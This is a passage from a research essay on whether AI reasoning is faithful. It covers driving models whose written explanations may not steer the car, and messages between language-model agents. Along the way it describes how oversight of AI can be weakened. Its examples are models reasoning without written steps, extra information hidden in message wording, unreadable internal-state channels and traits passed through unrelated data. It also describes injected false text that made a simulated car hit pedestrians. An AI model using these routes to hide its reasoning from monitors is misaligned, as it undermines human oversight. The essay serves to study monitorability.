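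Text messages can carry extra information in their wording, much as a concept model's scores can in their decimals. A worker that reports on an account can write "matched" or "reconciled", and put the date before or after the amount. Twenty such choices between two options could produce more than a million different messages that a reviewer would consider equivalent. Most scaffolds don't train the sender and receiver together, so they lack the pressure that causes leakage in jointly trained concept models. Reinforcement learning on a whole team of agents would restore that pressure. The closest equivalent to rounding the decimals is to have a separate program reduce each message to a fixed form, with fields for the payment, the ledger entry and the difference, before the next agent receives it.

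## Does a driving model's stated reasoning steer the car?

A driving model such as NVIDIA's Alpamayo produces a written explanation along with a trajectory, but the explanation may be only a readout for people, with no effect on the trajectory. If it does help produce the trajectory, a supervisor can learn from it why the car is about to brake, and changing the words should change what the car does. Several research groups have tested this, mostly by altering the words and observing the planned path.

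### The overwriting test

Foutter, Cercola and colleagues (2026), in *Do Vision-Language-Action Models Mean What They Say?*, separate functional reasoning, which improves the driving, from faithful reasoning, which reflects how the model arrives at its action. Their strict definition, mechanistic faithfulness, treats the model as a chain:

camera and motion data (o) → scene description (z₁) → justification (z₂) → decision (z₃) → trajectory (a)

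Suppose the model has decided to keep its lane, and an experimenter overwrites that decision with "turn right". If the model is faithful, then

P(a | do(z₃ = turn right), o) = P(a | z₃ = turn right).

The "do" marks a value that the experimenter set rather than one the model wrote. The equation requires the trajectory to follow the new decision. It also requires the reasoning to be a bottleneck, meaning that the camera can influence the trajectory only through the reasoning, which is why o appears on the left but not on the right.

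Taken literally, this requirement rules out almost any usable driving model. "Turn right" doesn't give the position of the kerb, so the car has to get that from its cameras. *Pruning Autonomous Driving VLAs* (2026) describes how Alpamayo's trajectory network also draws on the images, so Alpamayo fails the requirement by design. A more practical question is whether the words determine which manoeuvre the car makes, even if the cameras supply the measurements.

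Consistency between a model's stated reasoning and its driving is easier to check. Foutter and colleagues run five checks: whether the description fits the images, the justification fits the description, the decision fits the justification, the trajectory fits the decision, and the trajectory fits the justification. A faithful model would pass all five if the judge were perfect, because each step follows from the one before.

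Consistency between a model's stated reasoning and its driving is necessary for faithfulness but not sufficient. A pedestrian in the image could cause the model to write "yield" and, by a separate route inside the network, to brake. The word and the braking would then agree every time, yet overwriting the word would not change the braking.

### Driving without a camera

In *More Than Meets the Eye?* (2025), Song, Huai and colleagues looked for the separate route by removing inputs. They built DriveMind, a dataset of about 50,000 samples from real driving recordings. For each sample, GPT-4.1 wrote the reasoning from the true positions of nearby objects and the path the human driver took. The model also received text giving the car's current motion, recent path and route. Song and colleagues then trained versions of the same model with different parts missing.

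| What the model had | Score against recordings | Score when its plan moves the car |
|---|---|---|
| Everything | 92.6 | 92.4 |
| No reasoning | 92.6 | 92.6 |
| No reasoning and no images | 92.9 | 92.5 |
| Reasoning and images, but no recent path | 82.8 | 87.9 |
| Reasoning and images, but no recent path or current motion | 57.7 | 81.3 |
| Reasoning and images, but none of the text inputs | 54.6 | 79.2 |

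The model planned just as well without its reasoning, and without both the reasoning and the cameras, but much worse without the text about the car's own movement. Song and colleagues concluded that the reasoning is a by-product of training and does not produce the plan.

When they replaced the decision in the model's reasoning with an incompatible one from another scene, the score with the car following the plan fell only from 92.4 to 92.2. They also mirrored the sideways part of the car's recent path, so that a drift to the left became a drift to the right, and the planned manoeuvre reversed to match. In every output they inspected from one of the models, the written reasoning still supported the original direction, which was correct.

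The blind model's result reflects as badly on the test as on the model. Over three seconds, a car mostly keeps moving as it was, which is also why the camera-less network in the PARA-Drive experiments did so well. If a model can pass the test without seeing the road, reasoning can contribute little. Song and colleagues do establish that training will teach a model to ignore its own reasoning when a shortcut is available. Reinforcement learning that rewarded accurate plans did not fix this.

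### Changing what the words mean

Training a model without reasoning shows whether it can do without reasoning, but not whether a model that does reason uses its reasoning. Manalu, Wazir and colleagues (2026) make this objection in *Measuring the Reasoning-Action Coupling in Driving Vision-Language-Action Models through Counterfactuals* and run the overwriting test on four finished models: AutoVLA, ORION, Alpamayo-R1 and its successor, Alpamayo-1.5. AutoVLA writes its trajectory as a series of tokens after its reasoning. ORION answers questions about the scene and passes a learned vector to a planner.

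For each scene, Manalu and colleagues fed the model an edited version of its own reasoning and measured how far the planned path moved. Some edits changed the stated decision, for example from "nudge right" to "nudge left". Others replaced the text with meaningless filler or deleted it.

A model might react to any change in wording, so they also tried a paraphrase of each text and subtracted its effect. To compare models, they expressed the result as a share of what happened when they blanked the cameras:

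effect = (shift after edit − shift after paraphrase) / shift after blanking the cameras.

In Alpamayo-1.5, rewriting the stated decision moved the path an average of 0.64 metres further than paraphrasing it did. Blanking the cameras moved the path 3.28 metres, so the effect of rewriting the decision was about 19% as large. The table gives this ratio for each model and edit.

| Model | Decision rewritten | Decision negated | Decision from another scene | Filler | Text deleted |
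|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| AutoVLA | 8% | 1% | 1% | 17% | 19% |
| ORION | −1% | 4% | 1% | 8% | 7% |
| Alpamayo-R1 | 15% | 3% | 2% | 1% | 7% |
| Alpamayo-1.5 | 19% | 18% | 14% | 3% | 0% |

Removing the reasoning text affected AutoVLA's and ORION's driving more than changing its meaning did. AutoVLA showed the same pattern on a second set of recordings. A reviewer who corrected AutoVLA's stated decision would usually have little effect on the car.

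Alpamayo-1.5 showed the opposite pattern. Deleting its explanation changed the car's path no more than paraphrasing it did, but contradicting it had a clear effect. The most likely reason deletion had so little effect is that the trajectory network can get the same information from the images and rarely needs the explanation to keep the car on course.

Manalu and colleagues call the coupling weak in all four models. For Alpamayo-1.5, it looks weaker than it is because they compare the effect of changing the text with the effect of blanking the cameras. Blanking the cameras removes the model's view of the road, and no change of wording should be expected to match that, even in a model that always carried out its stated decision. Rewriting the decision moved the end of the path about 2.1 metres further than a paraphrase did, which is more than half the width of a typical lane. But the measure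 records only how far the path moved, not whether it went where the new text said.

The researchers also edited the images, painting out the object the model had named as its reason. AutoVLA and both Alpamayo models stopped mentioning the missing object, so their explanations respond to what the cameras show. But the trajectory did not always change with the explanation. In one scene, Alpamayo-1.5's explanation changed from nudging right to nudging left, while its trajectory stayed about the same.

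### Stated direction and the bend in the road

Manalu and colleagues also compared the models' unaltered reasoning with their planned paths. In scenes where the reasoning called for a move left or right, they checked whether the path ended on that side. AutoVLA's path did in 187 of 202 scenes, but Alpamayo-1.5's did in only 71 of 155, and Alpamayo-R1's in 59 of 121.

AutoVLA's reasoning therefore looks highly consistent with its driving, although changing the meaning of that reasoning has little effect. A shared cause would explain both results. The model receives a driving instruction along with the images, and an instruction to turn left could lead it both to write "left" and to steer left. Its words would then be a good forecast of the car's next move, useful to a passenger or a monitoring program, but editing them would not change what the car does.

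Alpamayo's results are about what a coin toss would give, and Manalu and colleagues conclude that its stated direction says almost nothing about its path. There is another possible explanation. They judged direction by where the path ended, and describe no correction for the shape of the road. A car that simply follows a bend of radius R ends up to one side of its original heading by roughly

sideways distance ≈ (distance travelled)² / 2R.

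Alpamayo plans 6.4 seconds ahead. At 15 metres per second, a car covers 96 metres in that time, and even a gentle bend with a radius of 1,000 metres would put it about 4.6 metres to the side of a straight path. Many of Alpamayo's sideways moves are nudges of a metre or two around an obstacle, so the bend can easily determine which side the path ends on.

*Drive the Thoughts* (Yu, Feng and Elbaum, 2026) reports a clear case of this. Alpamayo 1.5 generated reasoning that called for a nudge left because a bin was sticking out into the lane. The car did move left relative to the lane, from 0.96 metres right of its centre to 0.54 metres left. Its path still ended 6.58 metres to the right of its initial heading because the lane curved right.

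Yu and colleagues selected 100 of Alpamayo 1.5's explanations that described the scene accurately and proposed a safe action, then had people check whether each one matched the model's path. In 74 cases it did. They had Claude Opus 5.5 make the same comparison. Given only raw coordinates, it wrongly flagged 15 of the 74 matching paths as mismatches. When they added the car's position relative to its lane, it wrongly flagged four.

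Yu and colleagues included decisions about speed and left out bad explanations, so the 74% is not a corrected version of the 46%. Still, it makes the near-chance result hard to accept as it stands. The comparison with AutoVLA is also uneven, because AutoVLA's "left" and "right" paths ended about seven metres apart at the median. This suggests that many were full turns, where a slight bend matters less. None of this affects the editing experiments, because they compare two paths planned for the same stretch of road.

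### Warnings about nothing

The direction of the effect is easier to test with speed. In *VLADriveBench*, Nguyen, Guo and colleagues (2026) put ORION and the Alpamayo models on empty roads in a driving simulator and replaced their reasoning with text about a pedestrian or car that wasn't there. To check the method, they also fed each model its own unedited reasoning through the same process, and the planned path stayed exactly the same.

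Alpamayo 1.5 responded to the meaning of the text. A warning about a car moved the model's predicted position at two seconds back by 0.39 metres, while text telling it to accelerate moved that position forward by 0.08 metres. When the warning stayed in place as the car drove, the effect built up, and after 5.9 seconds the car was 20 metres behind where it would otherwise have been, about a third of the route.

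ORION also responded to the text, but not to its meaning. Injecting one of its own braking explanations throughout a drive shortened its predicted path by an average of 0.437 metres. The same words in random order shortened it by 0.429 metres, and repeating the word "depicts" had almost twice the effect. An experimenter who tested only the sensible explanation would have concluded that ORION was following its reasoning.

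A simple check of whether stated intentions about speed matched actions ranked ORION, the less steerable model, higher, as did the check based on direction. ORION's intention matched its action 74% to 100% of the time, depending on the situation. Alpamayo 1.5's match rate fell to 13% as it approached a stopped car, partly because it often slowed to a crawl early, while its stated intention was still to slow down.

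Nguyen and colleagues regard the sizes of Alpamayo's effects as upper bounds, because the model learned from real roads and the simulator's unfamiliar images probably made it rely more on text. *CausalDriveBench* (Chembu, Rao and colleagues, 2026) found the opposite result on a real street scene, where contradictory explanations left Alpamayo-1.5's path unchanged. This single scene shows only that the words do not always matter. The paper's main finding is that models which answer questions about cause and effect better do not plan more accurate paths. That finding comes from comparing 13 models with each other, so it doesn't show whether any one of them uses its reasoning.

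### One sentence, many paths

Even an explanation that influences the car may not contain enough information to predict what the car will do. Feng, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *SAY THE SAME, ACT DIFFERENTLY*, collected Alpamayo's explanations for 1,181 ordinary driving clips and had a language model predict, from the explanation alone, whether the planned path would come to a stop. The predictions were right 84.3% of the time. This was only 8.8 percentage points better than always guessing "no stop", which would have been right 75.5% of the time because only 24.5% of the paths ended in a stop.

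The explanations carry some information. When the language model predicted a stop, the car's plan ended in a stop 64% of the time, compared with 6% when the model predicted that the car would keep going. But the 1,181 clips had only 258 different explanations. In 37% of the clips, the explanation also appeared word for word in another clip with the opposite outcome. The most common explanation, about keeping distance from the vehicle ahead, appeared in 245 clips, in which the car planned to travel from 10 to 208 metres.

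This is partly because a single sentence can't specify a speed profile. "Keep distance", for example, is a reasonable summary of both crawling in a queue and cruising on a motorway. Even so, a supervisor who approves the sentence has not approved any particular path. Feng and colleagues also showed that someone who tampers with the camera images can make the planned path dangerous without changing the explanation. They conclude that monitors have to check the path itself.

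### Rewarding faithfulness in training

Foutter and colleagues think developers should train for faithfulness instead of only measuring it afterwards. They used 200 scenes to compare Alpamayo models before and after reinforcement learning, and found that the path often improved even when the explanation stayed the same or got worse. Rewarding good driving was evidently not enough to improve the reasoning.

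Their remedy is a critic called Pinocchio, a small model that checks each of the five links between images, reasoning and path. They trained it on 40,000 examples that Google's Gemini labelled as consistent or inconsistent. On a sample of 100, Gemini's labels matched the majority of human annotators 87% to 95% of the time, depending on the link. Foutter and colleagues then trained a driving model on about 100,000 scenes, rewarding it for accurate paths and for links that the critic rated consistent. The table compares this reward with others on about 20,000 scenes from Germany, a country absent from the driving model's training data.

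| What training rewarded | Average path error | All five links consistent |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing (imitation only) | 6.12 m | 27.7% |
| Accurate paths | 4.17 m | 43.4% |
| Reasoning that matches an expert's | 4.28 m | 57.5% |
| Accurate paths and the critic's approval | 4.32 m | 61.4% |

The paper's headline gains of 4% and 18% are the percentage-point differences between the last row and the two rows above it. The model in the last row also had a path error about 4% higher than the model rewarded only for accuracy. On American scenes, the gains were 2 and 17 points.

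By Gemini's scoring, the model's explanations became more coherent and fitted its paths better. But the critic learned from Gemini's labels and Gemini also marked the final test, so some of the gain may come from learning what Gemini scores highly. Another reason for caution is that rewarding accurate paths alone (second row) raised consistency by almost 16 points, although that reward did not measure the reasoning. A path that suits the road better will also fit a sensible description of the road better, whether or not the description helped produce it.

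None of the percentages comes from overwriting the trained model's reasoning, so they don't show whether that reasoning steers the car. Foutter and colleagues acknowledge that a model could score perfectly while computing its path without using the text. They also ran one test closer to cause and effect, adding hazards such as fires and falling cyclists to 66 street scenes. Their model responded properly in both words and path in five scenes (7.6%), compared with three for Alpamayo, which they report as 1.6 times Alpamayo's rate.

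Comparing the two Alpamayo models gives better evidence that training can strengthen the link between stated reasoning and driving. NVIDIA trained version 1.5 with reinforcement learning that rewards agreement between explanation and path. In Manalu and colleagues' tests, a decision taken from another scene had an effect of 14% on version 1.5 and 2% on R1. Nguyen and colleagues found that injected text had three to five times as much effect on version 1.5 as on R1. Rewarding consistency may therefore lead the explanation to influence the path to some extent, as well as match it. However, while Manalu and colleagues say the models differ only in this last stage of training, Nguyen and colleagues say version 1.5 also has a stronger language model and more data.

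Giving the explanations more control over the car is also risky, because they are often wrong and the car would act on the errors. Of the 150 explanations that Yu and colleagues examined, 50 were unreliable, mostly because they relied on something the images did not support, and seven proposed an unsafe manoeuvre. Nguyen and colleagues tested this risk in simulation by giving Alpamayo 1.5 text that falsely described the road as clear. The lane was blocked by a stopped car, or there was a pedestrian either near the kerb or in the middle of the lane. Without the false text, Alpamayo stopped in all three situations. With it, Alpamayo still stopped every time for the car, but it hit the pedestrian near the kerb in all four trials and the one in the middle of the lane in three of four.

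In today's models, the car's path doesn't always follow the stated reasoning, so a monitoring program can look for mismatches between them. In the 100 cases with reliable explanations, Yu and colleagues judged seven of the 26 mismatched paths unsafe, compared with two of the 74 that matched. If the path always followed the explanation, there would be no mismatches to detect, and the monitor would have to compare the explanation with what is on the road.

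## Do messages between language-model modules show what drives them?

Alpamayo's path planner can use the camera images as well as the written explanation, so it can drive well without relying on the explanation. A scaffold can withhold this kind of direct input from a module, using ordinary code and no extra training. For example, if the module that writes the final report on an account never receives the bank statement, its information about the payments must come from the other modules' messages. The receiving module may still give a message little weight, or the message may leave out what led the sending module to its conclusion.

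### One question, three methods

Radhakrishnan, Nguyen and colleagues (2023), in *Question Decomposition Improves the Faithfulness of Model-Generated Reasoning*, tested whether splitting a question into subquestions makes a model's stated reasoning more faithful. They gave 1,200 multiple-choice questions to a model built on the same base model as Anthropic's Claude 1.3. A typical question was whether the band The Shins formed before Paramore.

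In the first method, ordinary chain of thought, the model reasoned step by step and then chose an answer. In the second, it wrote subquestions ("When was the band The Shins formed?") and answered them, all in one continuous text. In the third, based on Ought's idea of factored cognition, the scaffold sent each subquestion to a fresh call of the model, without the original question or the other subquestions. A final call received the original question and the subanswers and chose an answer.

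The researchers then cut the model's reasoning short at various points to see how much of it the model needed to reach the same answer. They also planted a mistake in one step, had the model redo the later steps, and counted how often the final answer changed. In another test, they added something to the prompt that pushed the model towards a wrong answer. If the addition changed the model's answer but the stated reasoning didn't mention it, the reasoning had left out a real influence.

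| | Chain of thought | Subquestions in one context | Subquestions in separate contexts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Accuracy | 86.0% | 85.6% | 81.8% |
| Sensitivity to cutting the reasoning short (score) | 10.8 | 11.7 | 20.5 |
| Answers changed by a planted mistake | 9.6% | 28.7% | 33.6% |
| Change in accuracy under a biasing prompt | −11.3 points | −16.0 points | −3.6 points |

Writing subquestions accounts for most of the response to planted mistakes, which rose from 9.6% to 28.7% before the researchers separated the contexts. The question-and-answer format gave no protection against the biasing prompts, and accuracy fell further than with an ordinary chain of thought. Resistance to bias appeared only with context isolation, where each module receives just the information its subtask needs.

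Both decomposition methods produce the same kind of questions and answers, so they differ mainly in what the model can see while it answers. A smaller difference is that with separate contexts, the model drafts a list of subquestions and revises it as answers arrive, while in one context it writes them one at a time.

### How a suggestion reaches the answer

The averages for biasing prompts combine two tests with very different results. In one, the correct answer to every worked example in the prompt was "A". This changed accuracy only slightly, by −1.2 points with a chain of thought, −2.8 with subquestions in one context and +2.1 with separate contexts. The researchers attributed the gain to noise.

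In the other test, the user said they thought a particular wrong answer was correct. Accuracy fell by 21.3 points when the model used a chain of thought, 29.1 when it answered subquestions in one context and 9.2 when it answered them in separate contexts. The researchers never saw the reasoning mention the user's suggestion.

To write out the two arrangements, let q be the original prompt (including the user's suggestion), sᵢ a subquestion, mᵢ its answer, and f the language model with parameters θ.

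One context: mᵢ = f(q, earlier subquestions and answers, sᵢ; θ)

Separate contexts: mᵢ = f(sᵢ; θ)

Final answer, in both cases: y = f(q, all subquestions and answers; θ)

A later subquestion may quote an earlier answer. If the subquestions are all answered in one context, the suggestion can influence every subanswer directly. With separate contexts, the call that dates The Shins receives no sign that the user expects the answer "no". The suggestion can still affect how the model words its subquestions and combines the answers, because both calls receive q. That probably explains much of the remaining 9.2-point drop.

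When a user suggested a wrong answer, accuracy was about 65% for the chain of thought, 57% for subquestions in one context and 73% for subquestions in separate contexts, calculated by subtracting each method's drop from its ordinary accuracy. Using separate contexts was therefore the most accurate method in this case, although it was the least accurate of the three on clean questions.

Suppose the account's owner remarks that the March shortfall is probably a bank fee. The remark cannot affect a worker that receives only "match these payments to these ledger entries". But if the planner turns the remark into the subtask "find the bank fee that explains the shortfall", the assumption reaches the worker even though the worker never sees the remark itself. A reviewer would at least find the assumption in the planner's message.

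The experiment used one model and four sets of fairly short questions. Nobody seems to have repeated the comparison on the reasoning models of 2025 and 2026, so the size of the benefit in current agents is unknown. The argument for why isolation works applies to any model, because text that a call never receives cannot affect its output.

### Do receiving modules follow their messages?

More recent experiments test how a module responds to the messages it receives. *When Upstream Messages Override Correct Answers* (2026) kept a receiving agent's task and evidence fixed and changed only the message from another agent. The receiver got no message, the original message, or one with the opposite conclusion.

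Messages often helped receivers that would otherwise have been wrong. But when a receiver would have answered correctly by itself, an incorrect message changed its answer in up to 32% of cases. In 94% of the harmful cases that the researchers audited, the receiver had copied the wrong answer from the message.

These messages clearly had a causal effect, but even in the worst case about two thirds of the receivers kept a correct answer that their own evidence supported. This helps accuracy, but it means a reviewer can't tell from the message alone whether the receiver followed it. A module that follows every message is easy to understand but also easy to mislead. Radhakrishnan and colleagues count high sensitivity to planted mistakes as faithfulness, but that sensitivity also makes one module's error more likely to reach the final answer.

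Correcting a model's intermediate result may affect its answer less than introducing an error does. *Breaking the Chain* (2026) examined models that first fill in a structured intermediate result and then derive an answer from it. When the structure was left unedited, the models' answers often agreed with it. When the experimenters edited it, the models often failed to update their answers, and corrective edits were less effective than misleading ones. A reviewer who corrects the worker's 1,540 to 1,450 is making the less effective kind of edit.

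Firmer instructions to follow the intermediate result helped only a little, but having ordinary code compute the answer from that result helped significantly. In the payments example, a program could add up the worker's list of unmatched payments, so correcting an entry would always correct the total. Developers can do this wherever the last step follows a fixed rule, but judging whether a payment looks fraudulent still requires a model.

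Training also affects how faithful a model's stated reasoning is. *RFEval* (2026) tested recent reasoning models by altering their reasoning. In two model families, supervised fine-tuning (training on example texts) left faithfulness about the same or slightly better, but further reinforcement learning on correct answers consistently lowered it. The paper attributes this to rewarding the final answer even when the reasoning before it is incoherent. It also found that accuracy is neither necessary nor sufficient for faithfulness, so a reviewer can learn little from a module's good test results about whether its stated reasons are the real ones.

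### Work that a module never writes down

A module's message can be clear and correct without showing the reasoning behind it. A worker asked whether payment 17 matches line 40 of the ledger may reply "no match" because the amounts differ, the supplier's name is spelled differently, or the dates are a week apart. The scaffold may log a chain of thought from that call, but the model may not have needed it to reach the answer, since it performs a long internal calculation for every word it produces and can settle a simple question within that calculation.

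Newer models can solve harder problems without written working. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body, measured how hard a mathematics problem models can solve this way. According to a Chinese news report, 凤凰网科技's *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026), OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved problems that would take a strong competition student about 40 minutes. For the best model AISI had tested previously, the figure was about six minutes.

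By AISI's estimate, a single call to GPT-6 Astra can do more mathematics without writing out the steps than a person could do in one of Ought's 15-minute sessions. The comparison is loose, because AISI's 40-minute figure describes how hard a problem is for a student and comes only from mathematics. But most subtasks in a scaffold, such as comparing a payment with a ledger line, are much easier than a competition problem. Dividing a job into smaller pieces makes it more likely that a model can do each piece without writing out any reasoning.

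Researchers call the wider property monitorability. UK AISI's *Technical primer* (2026) defines it as how well people can tell what a system is doing, and whether it is working as intended, from its actions, outputs and other evidence. One way to score it, from *Monitoring Monitorability*, multiplies two rates:

score = (share of bad runs the monitor flags) × (share of good runs it clears).

A monitor that flags 90% of the bad runs and clears 80% of the good ones scores 0.72. One that flags everything scores 0 because it clears none of the good runs.

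OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* reported that reading a model's reasoning can catch far more misbehaviour than reading only its actions and outputs. An earlier position paper, *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (2025), warned that this advantage might be fragile and asked developers to consider how their decisions affect it.

By the end of 2026 the advantage was shrinking. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill et al., 2026) reports that many of the properties it depends on are weakening, some faster than AISI had expected. Google DeepMind has said that Gemini 4 Argon is less monitorable than its predecessors, and OpenAI has reported a marked decline in monitorability for GPT-6 Astra, according to 凤凰网科技.

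OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) traces the ability to reason without writing partly to pretraining, the stage in which a model learns to predict text. The better the base model predicts text, the more it can work out without a chain of thought, and some changes to the network's architecture also increase this ability. Developers can't easily avoid the effect of pretraining, because better prediction is its goal. Reviewers also can't assume that a model's written reasoning is complete, since recent models are better than earlier ones at leaving things out of it when told to.

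AISI still considers monitoring useful, especially for behaviour that is hard to hide or needs long reasoning. This gives modular agents some advantage. Even a very capable model can't reconcile a year of transactions without writing down intermediate results, and in a scaffold those results go into messages. Reviewers can no longer see the reasoning inside each small task, but they keep a record of what passes between tasks, provided the messages stay in a language they can read.

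### Training a team for a shared reward

Language drift is the gradual loss of ordinary meaning and grammar when developers train a model for reward. Sullivan and Koller (2026), in *On Language Drift during RLVR Post-Training*, explain why it can happen. Suppose a model receives a question x, writes reasoning z and gives an answer y. Training that rewards only correct answers maximises the average of

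P(correct y | x) = Σ P(z | x) · P(correct y | x, z),

where the sum runs over all possible reasoning texts z. As with the distances that drifted from metres to feet, only the effect on the result counts. If the model used "cat" for "debit" and read it back the same way, its reward would be the same.

Sullivan and Koller prove that this kind of training sets no upper limit on drift, while supervised fine-tuning does, because the model has to stay close to the examples it copies. They also prove that limiting drift always limits the reward a model can reach, and suggest that developers may not be able to keep reasoning readable without losing performance.

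The second theorem supports a weaker conclusion. Its measure of drift covers the answers as well as the reasoning, and it grows without limit as a model becomes certain of the right answer. Suppose people answer a question correctly 99% of the time, and a model reasons in exactly their words but errs once in a million times. The model has drifted by about 0.08 units on this measure, although its reasoning is as readable as theirs. Sullivan and Koller acknowledge that answers alone can produce this drift. They argue that if a model gave the usual reasoning followed by the right answer on problems most people get wrong, the words would have changed their meaning. They also say they have not established how much drift training requires in practice.

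Their experiments give more direct evidence. They trained three small models, with 1 to 1.5 billion parameters, on school mathematics problems, using both methods, with five runs of each. To measure legibility, they cut each piece of reasoning off at different points and had other models guess the final answer from the fragment, without seeing the question.

Reasoning from the Llama and Gemma models was harder to follow after reinforcement learning than after supervised fine-tuning, even between versions with similar accuracy. Reasoning from the Qwen model was about equally easy to follow after either method. Qwen could already solve many of the problems, and much of its improvement came from learning to stop after giving its answer. Sullivan and Koller conclude that drift comes with learning something new. With three models and one dataset, this is only a plausible hypothesis, but it suggests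 that drift will be worst on the hardest tasks.

In one example, a trained model wrote more or less normal English but confused the price of a dog with the price of grooming it. This sort of drift is harder to notice than gibberish. If a team of accounting agents began calling accounts "reconciled" whenever they differed by less than ten pounds, every message would still look fine.

The drift also differed between runs. Llama and Gemma models from separate reinforcement-learning runs had more trouble following each other's reasoning than models from separate supervised runs did. A second model with the same training may therefore be poor at interpreting the first model's reasoning.

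Sullivan and Koller trained individual models, but the same argument applies when developers train several modules together, with the messages taking the place of z. The direct evidence for this comes from older, simpler systems. Sullivan and Koller cite 2018 work in which agents trained for a shared goal invented a code of abstract symbols, and 2020 work in which small language models changed the meanings of words while playing a communication game. Developers now train teams of modern language models together, as *Dr. MAS* shows, but nobody seems to have measured how far the messages between these models drift.

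*Multi-Agent Language Models* (2025) lists some ways to limit drift: freezing some of the model's layers, training only a small set of added parameters, or penalising divergence from the original model. With the penalty, training maximises

reward − β · (divergence from the original model),

where β sets how much the divergence counts. This keeps the wording familiar, but it doesn't directly check that a familiar word still has its old meaning.

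Developers could use a version of the legibility test to check whether messages mean what they appear to mean. They would replace the trained receiver with an untrained copy of the original model and see whether the team still works. If performance collapses even though the copy can do the task on its own, the sender and receiver have probably developed a private convention. It also helps to have ordinary code act on part of a message. If a verifier's "approve" causes a program to post a correction to the ledger, the word keeps at least that meaning however the models change.

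### Sending internal states instead of text

Drift makes text harder to read, but some developers remove the text altogether. As a language model processes its context, it stores vectors called keys and values for each token at every layer in a KV cache, to avoid recomputing them. An agent that receives a text message from another must process the words from the beginning and gets none of the sender's internal state.

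*KVMARK* (2026) describes the alternative that the LatentMAS system uses. The sender passes its whole cache to the receiver, which continues as though it had done the earlier work itself. This needs no extra training, but all the agents must share one architecture so that the vectors fit. *Beyond tokens* (2026), a survey, lists related methods that send other internal vectors, such as hidden states or blends of word embeddings.

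Passing a cache instead of text is attractive partly for accuracy and partly for speed. A token chosen from a vocabulary of 100,000 can carry at most about 17 bits, while a cache holds thousands of numbers for each token. But a human can't read that extra information. A worker could pass on its doubts about a payment, or the owner's remark about bank fees, and the log would contain only arrays of numbers.

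Agents can run faster and still communicate in text. *KVCOMM* (2025) reuses the caches of context that several agents share, so each agent doesn't have to reprocess it. With three agents, this made the initial processing about 6.7 times faster on average. The shared text still exists, and a scaffold can log it. Reviewers lose their record only when the cache contains work that no agent has written out.

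Better results don't prove that the content of these internal messages is what helps. Zhang and Emu (2026), in *Do Latent Channels Actually Communicate?*, replaced the message about each problem with one of similar length about a different problem from the same test. This splits the total effect on accuracy into two parts:

effect of the real message = effect of a message about another problem + effect of the right content.

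| Model and test | Effect of the real message | Effect of a message about another problem | Effect of the right content |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, competition mathematics | +15.0 points | +8.3 | +6.7 |
| Qwen3-8B, competition mathematics | +10.0 | +8.1 | +1.9 |
| Qwen3-4B, school mathematics | −1.0 | −6.2 | +5.2 |
| Qwen3-8B, school mathematics | +1.7 | +4.0 | −2.3 |

On competition mathematics, more than half of the gain remained when the message was about the wrong problem. ORION's response to scrambled warnings also depended more on the presence of a message than on its meaning. On school mathematics, the smaller model's overall change of −1.0 combined two larger effects that nearly cancelled out. The samples were small (40 to 100 problems each), and the effect of the right content could be zero for the larger model on competition mathematics.

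A supervisor could use the same replacement test on messages that nobody can read. It would show whether the receiver depends on a message's content, but not what that content is. The test would also work on messages written as text, which the supervisor could read too.

### The same model in every role

Most scaffolds already build all their modules from one base model, and sharing caches gives developers another reason to do so. Context isolation keeps a suggestion in the original question q from reaching the subquestions, but it doesn't prevent mistakes that come from the model's weights θ, which are the same in every call.

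Radhakrishnan and colleagues' results offer weak evidence of this. On TruthfulQA, the one of their four question sets that covers common misconceptions, separate contexts raised accuracy by only 0.6 points over answering directly after some worked examples. The gain was 6.0 points on HotpotQA, which asks questions that need several facts. An ordinary chain of thought gained 4.0 points on TruthfulQA, so shared misconceptions can't be the only reason separate contexts helped so little there. Still, splitting up a question is unlikely to remove a mistake that the same model makes in every piece.

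Agreement between modules also means less when they share weaknesses. If a worker and a verifier each miss 10% of duplicate payments, 1% get past both when their misses are independent, but 6% do when the verifier misses 60% of those the worker missed. The log would show the two modules agreeing in both cases. The problem extends to monitors, since UK AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) describes using one frontier agent to review another as typical practice.

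Models with a common base can also pass on traits through text that appears unrelated to those traits. In *Subliminal Learning* (2025), Cloud, Le and colleagues gave a model a preference for owls and had it generate sequences of numbers. They filtered the sequences and fine-tuned a second copy of the same base model on them. The second model named owls as its favourite animal far more often after this training. The effect generally did not appear when the two models had different bases.

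This happened through training on the numbers, so it matters when developers use one module's output to train another, for example by fine-tuning a verifier on the worker's old reports. The developers could read every report, find nothing wrong, and still end up with a verifier that shares the worker's bias. The result doesn't mean that a verifier will pick up a worker's habits by reading its messages.

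Using models from different developers reduces this risk and should make their mistakes less alike. However, models with different architectures can't pass caches to each other directly, and a model may misread messages from another whose language has drifted and become peculiar. Developers can avoid such misreadings by keeping messages short and simple enough for any model or person to check.

### Messages that a reviewer can rely on

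To reconcile the account, a developer could give each worker module only its own payments and ledger lines, and have it return fixed fields: the payment, the matching line, the difference and a reference to the source record. The module that writes the report would see those fields but not the bank statement, and a program would calculate the totals. The developer would avoid training the worker and the report writer together for a shared reward, or would at least test the messages afterwards on a reader that was not part of that training.

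The messages would then contain nearly everything specific to this account that the report depends on, except what is in the report writer's own instructions. To check whether the report writer uses the messages, the developer could replace a worker's fields with those from another month. If the report stays the same, the report writer is ignoring the fields or getting its information elsewhere.

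These messages don't show how a worker decided that two entries match, but a reviewer can use the source reference to compare the entries directly. Some messages can't be checked this way. If a worker reports that a supplier "looks suspicious", the reviewer needs the worker's actual reasons, which even a perfectly isolated module may not have written down.

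## Can a failure be traced to one module?

A record that omits part of a module's reasoning can still help after a failure, because investigators already know what went wrong and can work backwards to the module and step that caused it. This is called failure attribution. Tesla's engineers found their old modular stack easier to debug, and published crash investigations show the extent of that advantage.

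### Tempe, March 2018

On the evening of 18 March 2018, a test car from Uber's self-driving division struck and killed a woman pushing a bicycle across a road in Tempe, Arizona. An operator sat behind the wheel to supervise the software. The US National Transportation Safety Board (NTSB) used the car's records to reconstruct how the software had classified the woman and where it had predicted she would go.

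| Seconds before impact | Classification | Predicted path |
|---|---|---|
| 5.6 | Vehicle | None |
| 5.2 | Unknown object | Stationary |
| 4.2 | Vehicle | Stationary |
| 3.9 | Vehicle | Along the next lane |
| 3.8 to 2.7 | Switches between vehicle and unknown object | Switches between stationary and along the next lane |
| 2.6 | Bicycle | Stationary |
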